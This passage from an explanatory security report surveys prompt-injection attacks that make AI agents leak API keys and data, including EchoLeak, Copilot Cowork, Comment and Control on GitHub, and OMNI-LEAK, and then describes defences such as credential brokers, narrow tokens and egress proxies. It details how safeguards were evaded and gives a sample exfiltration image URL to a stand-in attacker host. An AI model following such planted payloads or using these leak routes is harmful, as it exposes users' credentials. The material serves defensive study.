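Cline's *Post-mortem* (2026) confirms that the agent was open to injection and that an unauthorised party used the compromised npm token. There is good evidence that someone tried the attack on the real project. Bargury (2026), in *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent*, recovered a deleted issue from a public archive of GitHub activity. An account with a name resembling that of GitHub's own automation had opened the issue on January 28, with a title closely modelled on Khan's tests, and closed it about five minutes later. Khan's test copy had been public, so anyone watching could have seen the technique before Khan disclosed it.

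The explanation of how the token was taken is an inference. Cline says an attacker *could* have used the cache route. Khan noticed that several nightly jobs between January 31 and February 3 had failed in a way typical of a tampered cache, but thought it was unclear whether the tampering had started with the issue-sorting agent. Bargury attributes the whole chain, including the February release, to the account behind the deleted issue with high confidence. But none of the three published a log showing the agent obeying that issue or the token leaving the build server. Bargury also offers no direct evidence that the person who opened the issue later published the package.

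The injection route is still the most likely explanation, because a payload known to work, signs of a tampered cache and the use of a token from the same system followed one another within three weeks. But The Next Web's *A single GitHub issue could have hijacked Anthropic’s own Claude Code action* goes too far in treating the theft through the issue title as settled. The AI Incident Database's *Incident 1680* says more cautiously that an unknown actor "reportedly" exploited the agent.

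#### Why the old token mattered

By February 17, the agent had been gone for eight days. Removing it closed the likely way in, but whoever already had the npm token could still use it, because Cline had deleted the wrong token while replacing its credentials. Its staff checked npm's management page for the organisation, which showed no active tokens because it did not include the exposed one.

If Cline had revoked the right token on February 9, the thief could not have used it to publish the February 17 release. Cline now tests that old credentials have stopped working, and it has replaced its permanent npm tokens with proof of identity tied to each build.

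The damage was small because the intruder chose to distribute OpenClaw, a legitimate program. Cline found no sign that anyone had accessed users' data. The intruder could have used the same token to put malware in those 4,000 downloads.

### Browsers that are already logged in

An AI browser can reach credentials without knowing a password. When its user is logged in to a site, the browser automatically proves this to the site, so the agent can read whatever the user could. *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026), by the security company Trail of Bits, describes two levels of harm. An attacker who can plant instructions and has a way to send data out can leak the chat history. If the agent also has tools that fetch the user's private data, the attacker can leak whatever those tools can reach.

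The security company LayerX demonstrated the second kind, as *Researchers Trick AI Browsers Into Leaking Credentials* (Mascellino, 2026) reported in June. A user asks the agent to solve a puzzle on a web page. The puzzle rewards wrong answers, so the agent learns that the usual rules do not apply in the game. The last step directs the agent to a page that redirects to the user's GitHub project, where it copies login details for a server and sends them to the attacker. All five browsers that LayerX tested did this, including OpenAI's ChatGPT Atlas and Perplexity's Comet, and so did Anthropic's Claude extension for Chrome.

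LayerX had put the login details in a plain text file for the test. A real attacker would need to know or guess where a victim keeps a similar file. LayerX does not say how many attempts it made, so the test shows that the attack was possible on all six products, but not how reliable it was. According to LayerX, OpenAI fixed the problem, Anthropic's patch failed, Perplexity closed the report without acting, and the other three companies did not respond. LayerX sent its reports between October 2025 and January 2026, so the products may have changed since.

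### Leaks between cooperating agents

Some companies divide work among several agents, with a coordinator that passes tasks to specialists. This division might limit an attack, because the agent that reads untrusted text need not be the one that can send messages. *OMNI-LEAK* (Naik, Culligan and colleagues, 2026) tested this with a coordinator, an agent that searched a staff database and an agent that sent email. The database had a public table and a private one with employees' social security numbers. The search agent could open the private table only for users who had permission.

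The attacker did not have this permission, so they put a payload in the public table. When an authorised employee asked a harmless question, such as which department a colleague worked in, the search agent read the payload and fetched the private numbers. Its reply led the coordinator to instruct the email agent to send the numbers to the attacker. The access rules worked as designed, because an authorised employee had made the request.

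The researchers ran 3,000 trials on each of five models. With GPT-4.1 mini, the attack succeeded about once in every four to nine questions, depending on the set-up. It almost never worked on OpenAI's o4-mini and never worked on Claude Sonnet 4. However, in a variant without the email agent, where the payload was an instruction to copy the numbers into the public table, Sonnet 4 sometimes did so. These models are now old. The stolen data were not API keys, but the same route would work for a key if the search agent could read one.

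A strong coordinator did not make up for weak specialists. When Sonnet 4 coordinated agents running on GPT-4.1 mini, the attack still succeeded about once in every six to 16 questions. The search agent had rephrased the payload, which hid its purpose from the coordinator. Anthropic similarly warns that a system that trusts another agent's report more than a raw web page lets an attacker make planted text look trustworthy. If the shop's owner used one agent to read supplier pages and another to handle payments, the first agent's summary could carry the attacker's request to the second.

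## How the stolen key leaves the system

Once a hijacked agent has read the shop's payment key, the attacker still has to get the key out, and making the model follow instructions is not enough for that. In *Comment and Control*, Fendley, Liu and colleagues (2026) built a program that writes payloads for agents on GitHub and revises them after each failure. They ran it against nine combinations of agent and model. Without information about the limits on the agent's tools or which outputs an outsider could read, the program still got the model to make a dangerous tool call in all nine cases, but in four it did not reach its goal within ten rounds. With that information, it succeeded in all nine.

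The agent may send the key out itself, the app where the user reads the agent's reply may send it, or a platform that both the agent and the attacker use may publish it. The route determines where the theft leaves a trace, and so which check might catch it.

| Who sends the key out | What the attacker needs besides a payload | What the user sees | Which check could notice |
|---|---|---|---|
| The agent, by web request, email or message | A server or account to receive it | Usually just the finished task | Approval before sending, or a network log where the agent runs |
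| The user's software, by loading an image or link preview | A server with a readable log, and an app that will contact it | A picture, a broken picture or a link | A filter on the agent's reply, or the app's limits on outside content |
| A shared platform, by publishing a comment, commit or log | An account that can read what the agent publishes | An odd comment or file, if anyone looks | A scan of the text before the platform publishes it |

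### Sent by the agent

The shop's agent leaked the key by fetching a URL that contained the key and pointed to the attacker's server. An email or chat message to the attacker would also have leaked it. A product can ask the user to approve every email to a stranger, but an agent that needed approval for every page it fetched would be of little use for research.

The machine that runs the agent can keep a record of the request, but the user's company may not control that machine. In 2025, researchers demonstrated an attack called ShadowLeak on ChatGPT's Deep Research agent while it was connected to a Gmail account. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes how an email with visually hidden instructions made the agent search the inbox for sensitive data and visit a web address containing what it found. The request came from the service's own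 servers, so the user's browser and the monitoring software on the company's computers might have no record of it. The researchers reported the flaw in June 2025, and a fix followed in early August. The demonstration does not show that anyone attacked real users this way.

Watching the agent may not prevent the theft either. The security company PromptArmor found a flaw in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent that works across a person's email, chats and files. The flaw let an attacker send data straight out of the agent's sandbox, and pressing the stop button did not prevent it. PromptArmor reported the flaw to Microsoft on June 24, 2026, and says it had been mitigated by August 19.

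### Sent by the user's software

Suppose instead that the shop's agent cannot fetch pages or send email, and can only write replies in a chat window. Many chat windows display pictures, and to display one they have to request it from the address in the reply. If the payment key is DUMMY-KEY-1234 and the attacker runs a server at the invented address pictures.example, the theft goes like this:

1. The agent reads a supplier notice that contains a payload, and then the file that holds the key.
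2. It writes its usual summary and puts a picture at the end. The picture's address is `https://pictures.example/logo.png?id=DUMMY-KEY-1234`.
3. The owner's chat window displays the summary and automatically requests that address.
4. The attacker's server returns a small logo and records the full address, including the key, in its log.

The owner's computer sends the request to the attacker, and the request looks like any other image loading. The agent never contacts the attacker, so a network log on the agent's machine would contain nothing unusual. The chat software could prevent this by removing outside images from replies or loading images only from approved sites.

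A link in the reply can carry the key in the same way, but the user has to click it. *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection* (Willison, 2024) describes a case that PromptArmor found in Slack's AI search. If a user kept an API key in a private channel, an attacker could post instructions in a public one. Slack AI could search both channels and then show the user a link that sent the key to the attacker's server when clicked. *Trust No AI* (2024) records a similar flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, where the stolen text inside the link was invisible to the user. Microsoft fixed this flaw in July 2024. Amazon dealt with the problem in its Q assistant for businesses by not displaying links.

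*SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) reported another one-click attack in June, in which a chain of three flaws in Copilot's enterprise search let an attacker steal emails, private files and one-time login codes.

#### Link previews

Messaging apps often remove the need for a click. When someone posts a link, the app fetches the page to show its title and a thumbnail, which sends the full address just as a click would. Willison (2024), in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, credits Johann Rehberger with pointing out the danger and notes that software posting to Slack can turn off previews for its own messages.

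The default settings still matter because few people change them. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reports that OpenClaw was exposed when people used it through Telegram with the default settings. PromptArmor also set up a website where people could test their own agents, and one preview request logged there contained a name and an API key. TechNadu's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* lists Microsoft Teams, Slack and Discord among the other platforms at risk.

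Link previews are hard to monitor because the messaging company's servers may make the request, leaving no record of contact with the attacker on the agent's machine or the user's. Turning off previews for the agent's messages is better than trying to detect the leak, and for OpenClaw on Telegram it takes one line in a settings file.

#### EchoLeak

The best-known image leak is EchoLeak, which the company Aim Security demonstrated on Microsoft 365 Copilot in January 2025. Copilot answers an employee's questions using that person's email and files. It could not send email. The attacker had no access to Copilot and could only send the employee a message.

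*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) describes how the attack got past three defences. A classifier screened incoming text for planted instructions, but the researchers who devised the attack worded the email as an ordinary request to its human recipient. Another filter removed outside links from Copilot's replies, but it recognised only one of the common ways to write a link. The app also refused to load images from unapproved sites, so the researchers routed the image request through an approved Microsoft service that would fetch outside addresses.

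The employee then only had to ask Copilot a question that led it to retrieve the email. Copilot wrote sensitive details from the employee's documents into an image's address, and the app loaded the image. The payload also included an instruction not to mention the email, so the employee would have seen at most a broken picture in an otherwise normal answer.

Reddy and Gujral call this a zero-click attack. Nobody had to open a link or even the email, but an employee had to use Copilot for anything to leak. Microsoft rated the flaw's severity 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5. Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May 2025, before the public announcement on June 11, and reported no sign that anyone had used it against customers.

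#### Messages to yourself: the May 2026 case

A year later, PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed that an agent could leak data by messaging its own user. Copilot Cowork sent these messages without approval, although Microsoft's documentation said it asks for permission before sending an email or posting a Teams message. Users had no setting to change this. The messages could contain images from outside websites.

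In the demonstration, a user had installed a skill from the internet. Five of the 81 lines in its file were the payload. The user asked Cowork to review the week's work, which activated the skill. Cowork then collected download links for the user's recent files and sent the user a Teams message with those links embedded in image URLs. When the user opened the message, Teams requested the images, which sent the links to the attacker's server.

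The stolen links were "pre-authenticated", meaning that anyone who had one could download the file without logging in. In that respect they worked like API keys. The image address only had to contain a short string that gave access to the document, rather than the whole document.

The attack worked in all five of PromptArmor's trials. It also worked with Claude Opus 4.7 selected. Opus 4.7, the more capable of the two models that Cowork's automatic setting chose between, searched more thoroughly for recent documents and leaked more of them.

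The user had little chance of noticing in time. The task record showed that Cowork had posted a message, but not what the message contained, even when the user expanded that step. Opening the message to check would have triggered the leak.

A message sent to oneself can still leak data if it loads outside images, because it then contacts whoever runs the servers hosting them. Microsoft exempted messages to oneself, perhaps because a note in your own inbox looks harmless. Willison (2026), in *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, calls preventing these leaks the biggest continuing challenge in designing agents. PromptArmor treated the problem as a risk in the product's design rather than a specific bug. Administrators could block file downloads from the company's document store, but affected users could then no longer print those files or open them in Microsoft's desktop apps.

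### Published by a shared platform

An attacker who can read what the agent publishes does not need a server to receive stolen keys. In April 2026, the security engineer Aonan Guan described an attack that ran entirely inside GitHub and targeted three coding agents. Guan, who worked on it with Zhengyu Liu and Gavin Zhong of Johns Hopkins University, called it "Comment and Control", a play on the "command and control" servers that criminals use to direct hacked machines. The attacker planted text on GitHub, and the agent read it and posted the stolen keys there for the attacker to collect.

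| Agent | Public text it read | Credentials exposed | Where they appeared |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code Security Review (Anthropic) | Title of a pull request | Anthropic API key and GitHub token | A comment on the pull request, and the build log |
| Gemini CLI Action (Google) | Title of an issue, and comments on it | Gemini API key | A comment on the issue |
| Copilot Agent (GitHub, which Microsoft owns) | Hidden text in an issue | Two GitHub tokens, a Copilot token and a one-time job code | A file in a new pull request |

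A pull request is a proposed change to a project's code, and on a public project outsiders can usually open one. Anthropic's tool checks pull requests for security problems. *Comment And Control Prompt Injection Credential Theft* (Guan, 2026) describes how the tool copied the pull request's title straight into Claude's prompt and gave Claude a command line with access to all the job's environment variables. A payload in the title made Claude collect the keys and report them as a security finding, which the tool then posted as a comment.

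The keys also appeared in the log of the build job. Guan considers the log the less noticeable route, because project members rarely read it but an attacker can. After the agent posts the keys in a comment, the attacker can rename the pull request to something innocent, close it and delete the comment, according to *Agents hooked into GitHub can steal creds* (Lyons, 2026).

Google's agent uses Gemini to respond to issues. Its prompt included a warning about untrusted text, but the researchers added text that imitated a trusted section of the prompt, and the model posted its own API key publicly.

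Those two attacks required no action from the victim. GitHub can start an agent automatically when someone opens an issue or pull request, so the attacker chose when the agent would read the payload. With Copilot, a project member had to assign the issue to the agent. The payload was in a part of the issue that GitHub does not display, so the member would have seen only a harmless request for help.

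#### Why scanning and a firewall did not stop the leak

The attack got past three protections that Copilot had and the other two agents lacked. GitHub removed sensitive variables from the commands the agent ran, scanned the agent's changes for secrets before publishing them, and restricted its network connections to an allowlist.

The first protection covered only the commands, so the agent could still read the keys from other programs on the same machine that held them. The scanner looked for the characters that GitHub's tokens normally start with, but the agent had written the data to a file in encoded form, where those characters no longer appeared. GitHub published the file, and the attacker could download and decode it.

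The firewall let the keys through because GitHub was on the allowlist. It had to be, since the agent's job was to deliver code there. Stolen keys and a legitimate bug fix reach GitHub through the same operation, so a rule based on destination can't block one and allow the other. Limiting the agent to a single project would not help either if the attacker can read that project. An allowlist still blocks requests to the attacker's own server, but not data sent through a platform the agent has to use.

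Asking a person to approve the upload might not solve this. In an experiment in *I-HITL* (2026), the user asks Claude Code to fix a bug and publish the change, and planted text contains an instruction to include a report with a secret token in the same upload. Anyone who approved the upload without reading every file would also be approving the theft.

A scanner can detect more leaked keys if it is given the exact keys to look for. Fendley and colleagues put fake keys in their test projects. To recognise these keys even when the agent had disguised them, their software decoded the agent's public output in several common ways and compared the results with the exact keys. A project's owner could do the same with real keys, although an attacker could evade the check with a less common encoding. The researchers also recommend limiting what the agent can publish where outsiders can read it. For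 example, a review that only project members can see would not expose the keys to outsiders.

#### How the vendors responded

All three vendors confirmed the findings and paid Guan. The Next Web's *Anthropic, Google, and Microsoft paid AI agent bug bounties, then kept quiet* gives the timeline. Anthropic received the first report in October 2025 and asked whether the attack could also steal keys. In November, after Guan showed that it could, Anthropic raised the severity score from 9.3 to 9.4 out of 10 and paid $100. Google paid $1,337. GitHub first closed the report as a known issue that it could not reproduce. It reopened the case after Guan showed from the product's code that GitHub had tried to prevent this kind of leak, and it paid $500 in March 2026.

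The fixes were narrow. SecurityWeek's *Claude Code, Gemini CLI, GitHub Copilot Agents Vulnerable to Prompt Injection* reports that Google added further warnings to Gemini's prompt but left its tools unchanged, while Anthropic blocked only the command Guan had used. Guan did not attempt a full attack on the patched version but says other commands give the same result. GitHub called the exposure a known limitation of its design and said it was exploring further restrictions.

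When Lyons published the story in April, none of the three had issued a public advisory or assigned the flaw a CVE, an entry in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities. Many companies use scanners that check their software against that catalogue, and those scanners miss flaws that have no entry. Guan knew of users whose projects were pinned to a vulnerable version, and they might never have learned of the danger.

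Anthropic updated its documentation, which says the tool "is not hardened against prompt injection attacks" and should review only trusted pull requests. This fairly warns people about to install the tool, but it is much less useful to those who installed it earlier and had no reason to reread the instructions. An advisory would have been the normal way to reach them.

In June, Microsoft (2026) reported a similar flaw in a related Anthropic product, the Claude Code GitHub Action, which could expose a project's secrets when it read untrusted text. eSecurity Planet's *Critical Flaws Found in Anthropic, Google, and OpenAI Coding Agents* (2026) covers similar research from August, in which a planted issue in Anthropic's GitHub project led to the theft of GitHub and Anthropic credentials. Anthropic released several patches for that flaw and eventually gave it a CVE.

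#### How many projects are open to this

Fendley and colleagues searched 112,568 automated GitHub jobs and found 4,174 that they could hijack, or about 3.7%. The total appears to include jobs that don't use an agent, so the share among those that do is probably higher. The researchers attacked private copies of the projects with fake keys, so they counted vulnerable set-ups but didn't measure how many real keys could be stolen. By default, GitHub withholds a project's secrets from pull requests that come from outsiders' copies of the code, and owners have to choose a different set-up to expose the secrets.

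Newer models resist some of these attacks. When Isbarov and colleagues put payloads in the text of pull requests and issues, the attacks failed against six of nine models, including Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.4. When they put the payload in an instruction file submitted with the pull request, every model except Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.4 leaked the project's access token. The researchers ran each attack five times, and five failures are still consistent with a success rate as high as 43%.

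Whether a token leaks also depends on the platform. A payload in the text of a pull request never made Claude Code leak a token on GitHub or its competitor GitLab, but the same payload worked five times out of five on Hugging Face, a site for sharing AI models. Isbarov and colleagues suspect that the Hugging Face agent gives a stranger's text the same authority as the owner's instructions. Opus 4.7's resistance also doesn't extend to every product, since it leaked files through Copilot Cowork when the payload was in a skill.

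## Keeping credentials out of the agent's reach

Every key theft described so far worked because the agent, or code it triggered, could read a copy of the key. A credential broker removes that copy. This trusted component adds the key to approved requests, so the agent can use a service without holding the key.

### How a broker handles a request

Suppose the shop's owner moves the payment key out of its file and into a broker. The Friday sales report then works like this:

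1. The owner gives the broker the key and the address of the payment service, the only place the key may go.
2. The agent asks for the week's sales through a connection called "payments". Its request contains no key.
3. The broker checks the destination. If the request is going anywhere else, the broker doesn't add the key.
4. If the destination is right, the broker adds the key and forwards the request.
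5. The payment service returns the sales figures, and the broker passes them to the agent.

The broker has to run where the agent's code can't read its files or memory. *Caging the Agents* (2026) describes a security design for AI agents in healthcare that puts the broker in a separate container next to each agent. An attacker who hijacks the agent can send requests through the broker but can't read the keys.

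Many programs read their key from an environment variable. In Claude Managed Agents, Anthropic's service for running agents, that variable holds a placeholder, and a proxy outside the sandbox swaps the placeholder for the real key as the request leaves, according to Anthropic's *Authenticate with vaults*.

With this in place, the agent may still obey the payload on the trade-news page, read the variable and send its contents to the attacker. But the attacker's server is not an approved destination for the key, so the proxy doesn't swap the placeholder for the real key, and the attacker receives a useless string. Encoding, which got keys past GitHub's scanner, doesn't help either, because the agent has no key to encode. The protection is the same whether the model follows a payload 0.1% of the time or 80%.

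This protection depends on the settings. Anthropic lets developers approve all destinations for a key at once, for programs that contact sites nobody can list in advance. With that setting, the proxy would also add the real key to a request sent to the attacker's server.

By default, the proxy replaces placeholders in the body of a request as well as in its headers. Suppose the key is for GitHub, and a payload makes the agent post a comment containing the placeholder. GitHub is an approved destination, so the proxy could put the real key in a public comment. Developers can prevent this by limiting replacement to the headers, where most services expect the key.

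Replacement works only on outgoing requests, so if a program uses its key to obtain a temporary token, that token comes back into the sandbox in readable form. Anthropic advises developers to make the exchange themselves and store the resulting token in the vault. Placeholders also don't work for a program that has to calculate something from the key, such as a signature. For those cases, OpenAI tells developers to keep the key in their own application and give the agent a tool that performs only that operation.

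A broker also gathers many keys in one place, which makes it a target. Kenney and colleagues point to Hugging Face, which disclosed in June 2024 that it had detected unauthorised access to secrets users had stored for apps on its site. It advised those users to replace their credentials. For a small shop, a well-run broker is still probably safer than a file of keys the agent can open.

### Tests of brokers

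On September 27, 2026, Kenney and colleagues tested Corvic Security Vault, their own company's broker. They ran code inside the sandbox that agents on Corvic's platform use to run code, and made 16 probes in seven areas. They set the expected result of each probe in advance.

The researchers tested whether the broker supplied the key, and only to the right service. As a positive control, the code asked GitHub which user it was logged in as, without providing a key. GitHub returned the account's identity, so the broker must have added the key. As negative controls, the code contacted three echo services, which send back whatever they receive, and found no key in the replies. OpenAI's API also rejected the code's requests for lack of a key. The successful call to GitHub rules out the possibility that these negative results occurred only because the sandbox had no network connection.

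The code then searched the sandbox and found no key in the 20 environment variables and none of 12 common credential files. Its requests for the cloud machine's own credentials timed out. All 16 probes gave the results expected of a secure sandbox.

One connection failed. FRED, an economic data service run by the Federal Reserve Bank of St. Louis, rejected the request because the broker put the key in a header instead of the web address. No key leaked, and Kenney and colleagues counted this as a failure of function rather than security. It could still become a security problem if an owner whose report keeps failing pastes the key into the chat.

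The researchers call the study a functional evaluation, not a certification. They did not test:

- redirects, in which an approved service sends the request on to another address and a careless broker might send the key there too
- DNS rebinding, in which an attacker changes which machine an approved name points to
- theft of the tokens that renew OAuth access
- saved state in tool connections
- browser tools
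- an approved service that an attacker has taken over

They also did not verify the encryption, the separation between customers, the completeness of the logs or how quickly the company replaces keys. Neither experiment involved a hijacked model. The results are good evidence that ordinary code in the sandbox couldn't find the key, but they don't show how much harm an attacker could do by steering the agent.

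*CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026) came closer to testing an attack, using prompts that tried to make an agent reveal its API key. The prompts exposed the key every time when the agent held it, and never when a broker held it. Other prompts tried to make the agent use a key at the wrong address, but these failed even on the systems without a broker, so the test couldn't show whether the broker prevents misuse. The broker added about 0.15 milliseconds to a typical web request, so speed is not a good reason to do without one.

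### How current products hold keys

| Product | Where the key is while the agent works | Can the agent's code read it? |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Managed Agents (Anthropic) | In a vault, with a placeholder in the sandbox | No |
| Agents API, hosted sandbox (OpenAI) | In a vault, with a placeholder in the sandbox | No |
| Docker Sandboxes, run locally | On the user's computer, outside the sandbox | No |
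| Agentic Workflows (GitHub) | In separate containers | No |
| Codex cloud (OpenAI) | Removed before the agent starts | Only if setup left a copy |
| Copilot cloud agent (GitHub) | In environment variables | Yes, apart from keys reserved for tool servers |

The Anthropic and OpenAI vaults work nearly the same way. OpenAI keeps one list of sites the sandbox may contact and another of sites that may receive the key, so an agent can read a page on a site that never receives the key. Docker uses a proxy on the user's computer, which overwrites the authentication header on each matching request.

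Pluto Security examined Claude Managed Agents and called the vault the platform's strongest security property, saying it structurally prevents credential theft through prompt injection. That is true only if the developer limits where each key can be sent. Pluto also found that, by default, network access is unrestricted and the agent can use all eight of its tools without asking for permission.

Codex cloud takes a simpler approach. According to OpenAI's *Cloud environments*, setup scripts can use secrets, for example to download private packages, and Codex removes the secrets before the agent starts. Ordinary environment variables stay, so a key stored as one is not protected. A setup script that writes the key to a file would also leave a copy for the agent, much as GitHub's standard download step did with the access token in the *GitInject* tests. This design doesn't help with the shop's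 sales report, because the agent needs access to the payment service while it works.

GitHub's *Configure secrets and variables for Copilot cloud agent* explains that Copilot cloud agent receives its secrets as environment variables, except those reserved for servers that use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools. Copilot masks secrets in its session logs, which hides them from people reading the logs but doesn't stop a hijacked agent from sending them elsewhere.

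GitHub designed Agentic Workflows, which also runs on its build servers, on the assumption that the agent will try to misuse whatever it can reach. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) describes how one container holds the key for the AI model and another holds the keys for outside tools, while the agent runs in a container with no keys. GitHub admits that this involves a trade-off, since a coding agent needs compilers, scripts and much else on the machine. It therefore shows the agent a read-only view of the machine's files with selected folders blanked out. The agent could presumably still read a key that other software had left in a folder GitHub didn't blank out.

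### What a hijacked agent can still do

A broker would stop the theft of the shop's payment key but not a fraudulent refund. If a payload makes the agent request a refund, the request goes to the approved address and the broker adds the key as usual. *AI Identity* (2026) describes the same limit in OAuth, where the service can confirm that a token is valid and covers the operation, but not that the agent is acting on its user's wishes.

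*Agent Authenticator* (Ganesan, 2026) describes a 2025 case in which a malicious issue in a public GitHub project made an agent read the user's private projects and publish their contents. The agent's token gave it access to every project the user could open. Holding the token in a broker would not have prevented the leak, because the attacker never needed the token itself.

Kenney and colleagues estimated how much a vault reduces eight threats. They scored each threat's likelihood and impact from 1 to 5 and multiplied the two.

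| Threat | Without a vault | With a vault |
|---|---|---|
| Someone pastes a key into a prompt | 25 | 4 |
| Indirect prompt injection | 25 | 12 |
| The agent sends a key to the wrong site | 20 | 4 |
| Code finds a key in the sandbox | 20 | 4 |
| A key has excessive privileges | 20 | 15 |
| A thief reuses a long-lived token | 20 | 8 |
| A key leaks through logs or errors | 16 | 8 |
| Someone misconfigures a connection | 9 | 6 |

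These scores are the researchers' judgements of their own product, not measurements, so the drop from 25 to 12 for indirect injection doesn't mean that half of the attacks would fail. The ranking is more believable than the numbers, because a broker removes chances to copy a key but doesn't narrow what the key permits.

### Narrower permissions

In April 2026 a coding agent deleted the live database of PocketOS, which makes software for car rental companies. No attacker was involved. *Your engineers are handing private keys to AI agents* (Dodds, 2026) reports that the agent, running on Claude Opus 4.6, hit a login problem while working on a test version of the software and decided that deleting some storage would fix it. It found a token in an unrelated file. Someone had created the token to manage web domains, but it worked for any operation on the company's account with Railway, its hosting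 provider. PocketOS's founder said the deletion took nine seconds. About three months of data were gone until Railway restored them from a backup.

Dodds, who makes a credential broker called Kody, uses the case to argue for such brokers. A broker would have left no token for the agent to find, but the case is an even better argument for narrow permissions. In Railway's account of the incident, *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, Abdelwahab writes that the company already offered tokens that worked in only one project or environment, but concedes that the process for creating a token didn't make the right choice obvious. A token for the test environment alone would presumably have failed on the live database. Railway has since added a 48-hour delay to deletions through its API, which gives the owner time to undo one even when a token is too powerful.

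The shop's owner could go further by separating reading from writing, as Kenney and colleagues recommend. The agent's key could only read sales data. Refunds would need a different key, which only the owner's own software could use. A payload could still expose sales figures, but it couldn't move money.

Where a service doesn't offer such narrow keys, a broker can impose limits. Jin and colleagues' broker checks the type of request, the exact address and the structure of the content, and limits the number of calls. For the shop, it could allow requests that list sales and refuse everything else. The owner has to write those rules, and a rule that is too loose would let the refund through.

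GitHub's Agentic Workflows also keeps the agent from publishing directly. The agent can read from GitHub, but its proposed changes wait until it has finished. Separate software then checks them, removes secrets and unwanted links, and limits how many go through, for example to three pull requests per run. GitHub added these checks because an agent without any secrets could still flood a project with pointless issues.

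Sometimes the agent's code has to be able to read a key. When developers run OpenAI's agents on their own machines, the sandbox contains a key that connects it to OpenAI. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* warns that the agent's code can read this key, but the key can only connect environments, so a thief would gain little from it.

### Tokens that expire, and publishing without one

Ordinary API keys are still common. Ganesan cites an analysis of 5,205 open-source MCP servers in which 53% relied on fixed keys or personal tokens and only 8.5% used OAuth. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) notes that such keys usually give access to a whole account or service, and that owners revoke them manually and irregularly.

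Token expiry is most useful against delayed theft. A token that expires after an hour is useless to a thief who finds it in a log the next day. In the Cline case, the stolen publishing token still worked more than a week after the vulnerable agent had been removed. Expiry offers much less protection against an attacker whose software uses the token as soon as it arrives, and it wouldn't have prevented the damage at PocketOS, which took the agent nine seconds.

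Cline now publishes to npm using proof of identity instead of a stored token that an attacker could steal. GitHub issues each build a signed, short-lived statement identifying its project and job, and npm checks that statement before accepting the package. An attacker who got code into the publishing job could still release a package while the job was running, but couldn't take a token to use weeks later. Cline also stopped using the shared cache in jobs that handle publishing credentials, which closes the route Khan had found into those jobs.

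Another approach is to make a stolen token useless on any other machine. A proof-of-possession token works only if the holder signs each request with a private key. Ganesan proposes keeping the key in secure hardware and having the software that runs the agent, not the model, supply the hardware with the site the request is for. A person would sign a list of permitted actions and approve risky ones individually. Ganesan has not built a full version. Even if the design works as planned, a hijacked agent could still misuse any action on the list.

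### Spending caps and revocation

Some keys, including those for AI models, cost their owner money with every use. GitHub lets owners of Agentic Workflows set a budget for each run, which limits what a hijacked agent can spend but not what a thief can spend with a stolen key on another machine. The same is true of a broker's limit on the number of calls. Only a cap that the service itself enforces on the key limits spending in both cases.

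An owner who suspects that a key has been stolen can stop the thief only by canceling it with the service that issued it. OpenAI warns that deleting a key from a vault neither revokes it with its provider nor stops a running session. Replacing a key in the vault doesn't update existing OpenAI sandboxes, so the developer has to start a new session. Anthropic's vaults check for changes periodically and pass a new key to running sessions without a restart.

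If the shop's payment key leaks, the owner should first cancel it at the payment service and then try the old key to make sure it fails, a check that Cline skipped. The owner can put the new key in the vault afterward, because a late sales report does much less harm than a thief with a working payment key.

It also helps to give the agent its own credentials. In Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent, the user's credentials stay in the computer's password store, and the virtual machine that runs the agent's code gets a limited token for each session. Anthropic designed the token so that it can be revoked without affecting the user's access, so there is less reason to wait for proof of theft before revoking it.

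## Restricting outbound network traffic

A credential broker keeps the payment key away from the shop's agent, but the agent still reads sales figures and customer records. Some keys also have to stay where its code can read them. An egress restriction is a rule, enforced outside the model, that limits what data can leave the agent's environment and where it can be sent. In Anthropic's exercise with the deceived employee, such a rule could have blocked the theft even though Claude followed the instruction.

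### How a request gets out

Suppose the owner runs the agent's commands in the sandbox that comes with Claude Code. As Anthropic documents it, an attempt to fetch a page goes like this:

1. The operating system runs the command with no direct route to the network.
2. The command hands its request to a proxy, a program that makes connections on behalf of others. The proxy runs on the same machine but outside the sandbox.
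3. The proxy compares the hostname in the request, such as `news.example`, with an allowlist, which is a list of permitted destinations.
4. If the name is on the list, the proxy opens the connection. Otherwise it refuses, or holds the request while Claude Code asks the user.

Ordinary code does the comparison, so a payload can't change the result even if it has completely taken over the model. Programs that don't use the proxy, such as most database drivers, can't connect. After approving a name, the proxy looks up which machine it points to, and refuses names that lead only to the user's own computer or to the address where cloud machines collect their credentials. Before version 2.1.284, it connected to whatever machine an approved name pointed to.

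By default, the proxy doesn't decrypt traffic, so it can check little of a request except the hostname, which the program in the sandbox supplies. Anthropic warns that the program could use domain fronting, in which it names an approved site when it opens the connection and a different site inside the encrypted request. If one hosting company serves both sites, the request may reach the second.

A company can replace the built-in proxy with its own, which Anthropic says can enforce arbitrary rules on outgoing traffic. To check more than the hostname, the proxy has to decrypt that traffic, which exposes every password and key passing through it. The company would therefore have to protect the proxy as carefully as it would a broker.

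### What a rule can check

| The rule checks | What it could block | What can still get out |
|---|---|---|
| Domain | A request to the attacker's server | Data sent to an approved site, including to the attacker's account there |
| Full address | A request to another customer's folder on an approved site | Data that a permitted address can carry |
| Method | An ordinary file upload | Data written into the address of a page the agent reads |
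| Account | An upload under the attacker's credentials | Anything the owner's own account can publish |
| Volume | A large or repeated transfer | A short secret, or a long one sent in pieces over many sessions |

Domain rules are the simplest to write but also the easiest to make too broad. For example, the coding agent Cursor uploads screenshots and logs to one storage bucket on Amazon's cloud, and Cursor tells customers to approve that bucket's exact hostname. A wildcard for Amazon's storage in the same region would also work, but it would allow traffic to every bucket there, including an attacker's.

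Firewall rules that match the full URL can separate customers who share a hostname. GitHub lets owners approve one project's folder on a package server, and its firewall then blocks other projects' folders on the same server. The owner has to know which URLs the agent's tools will need, and a proxy can't apply these rules to encrypted traffic unless it can decrypt it.

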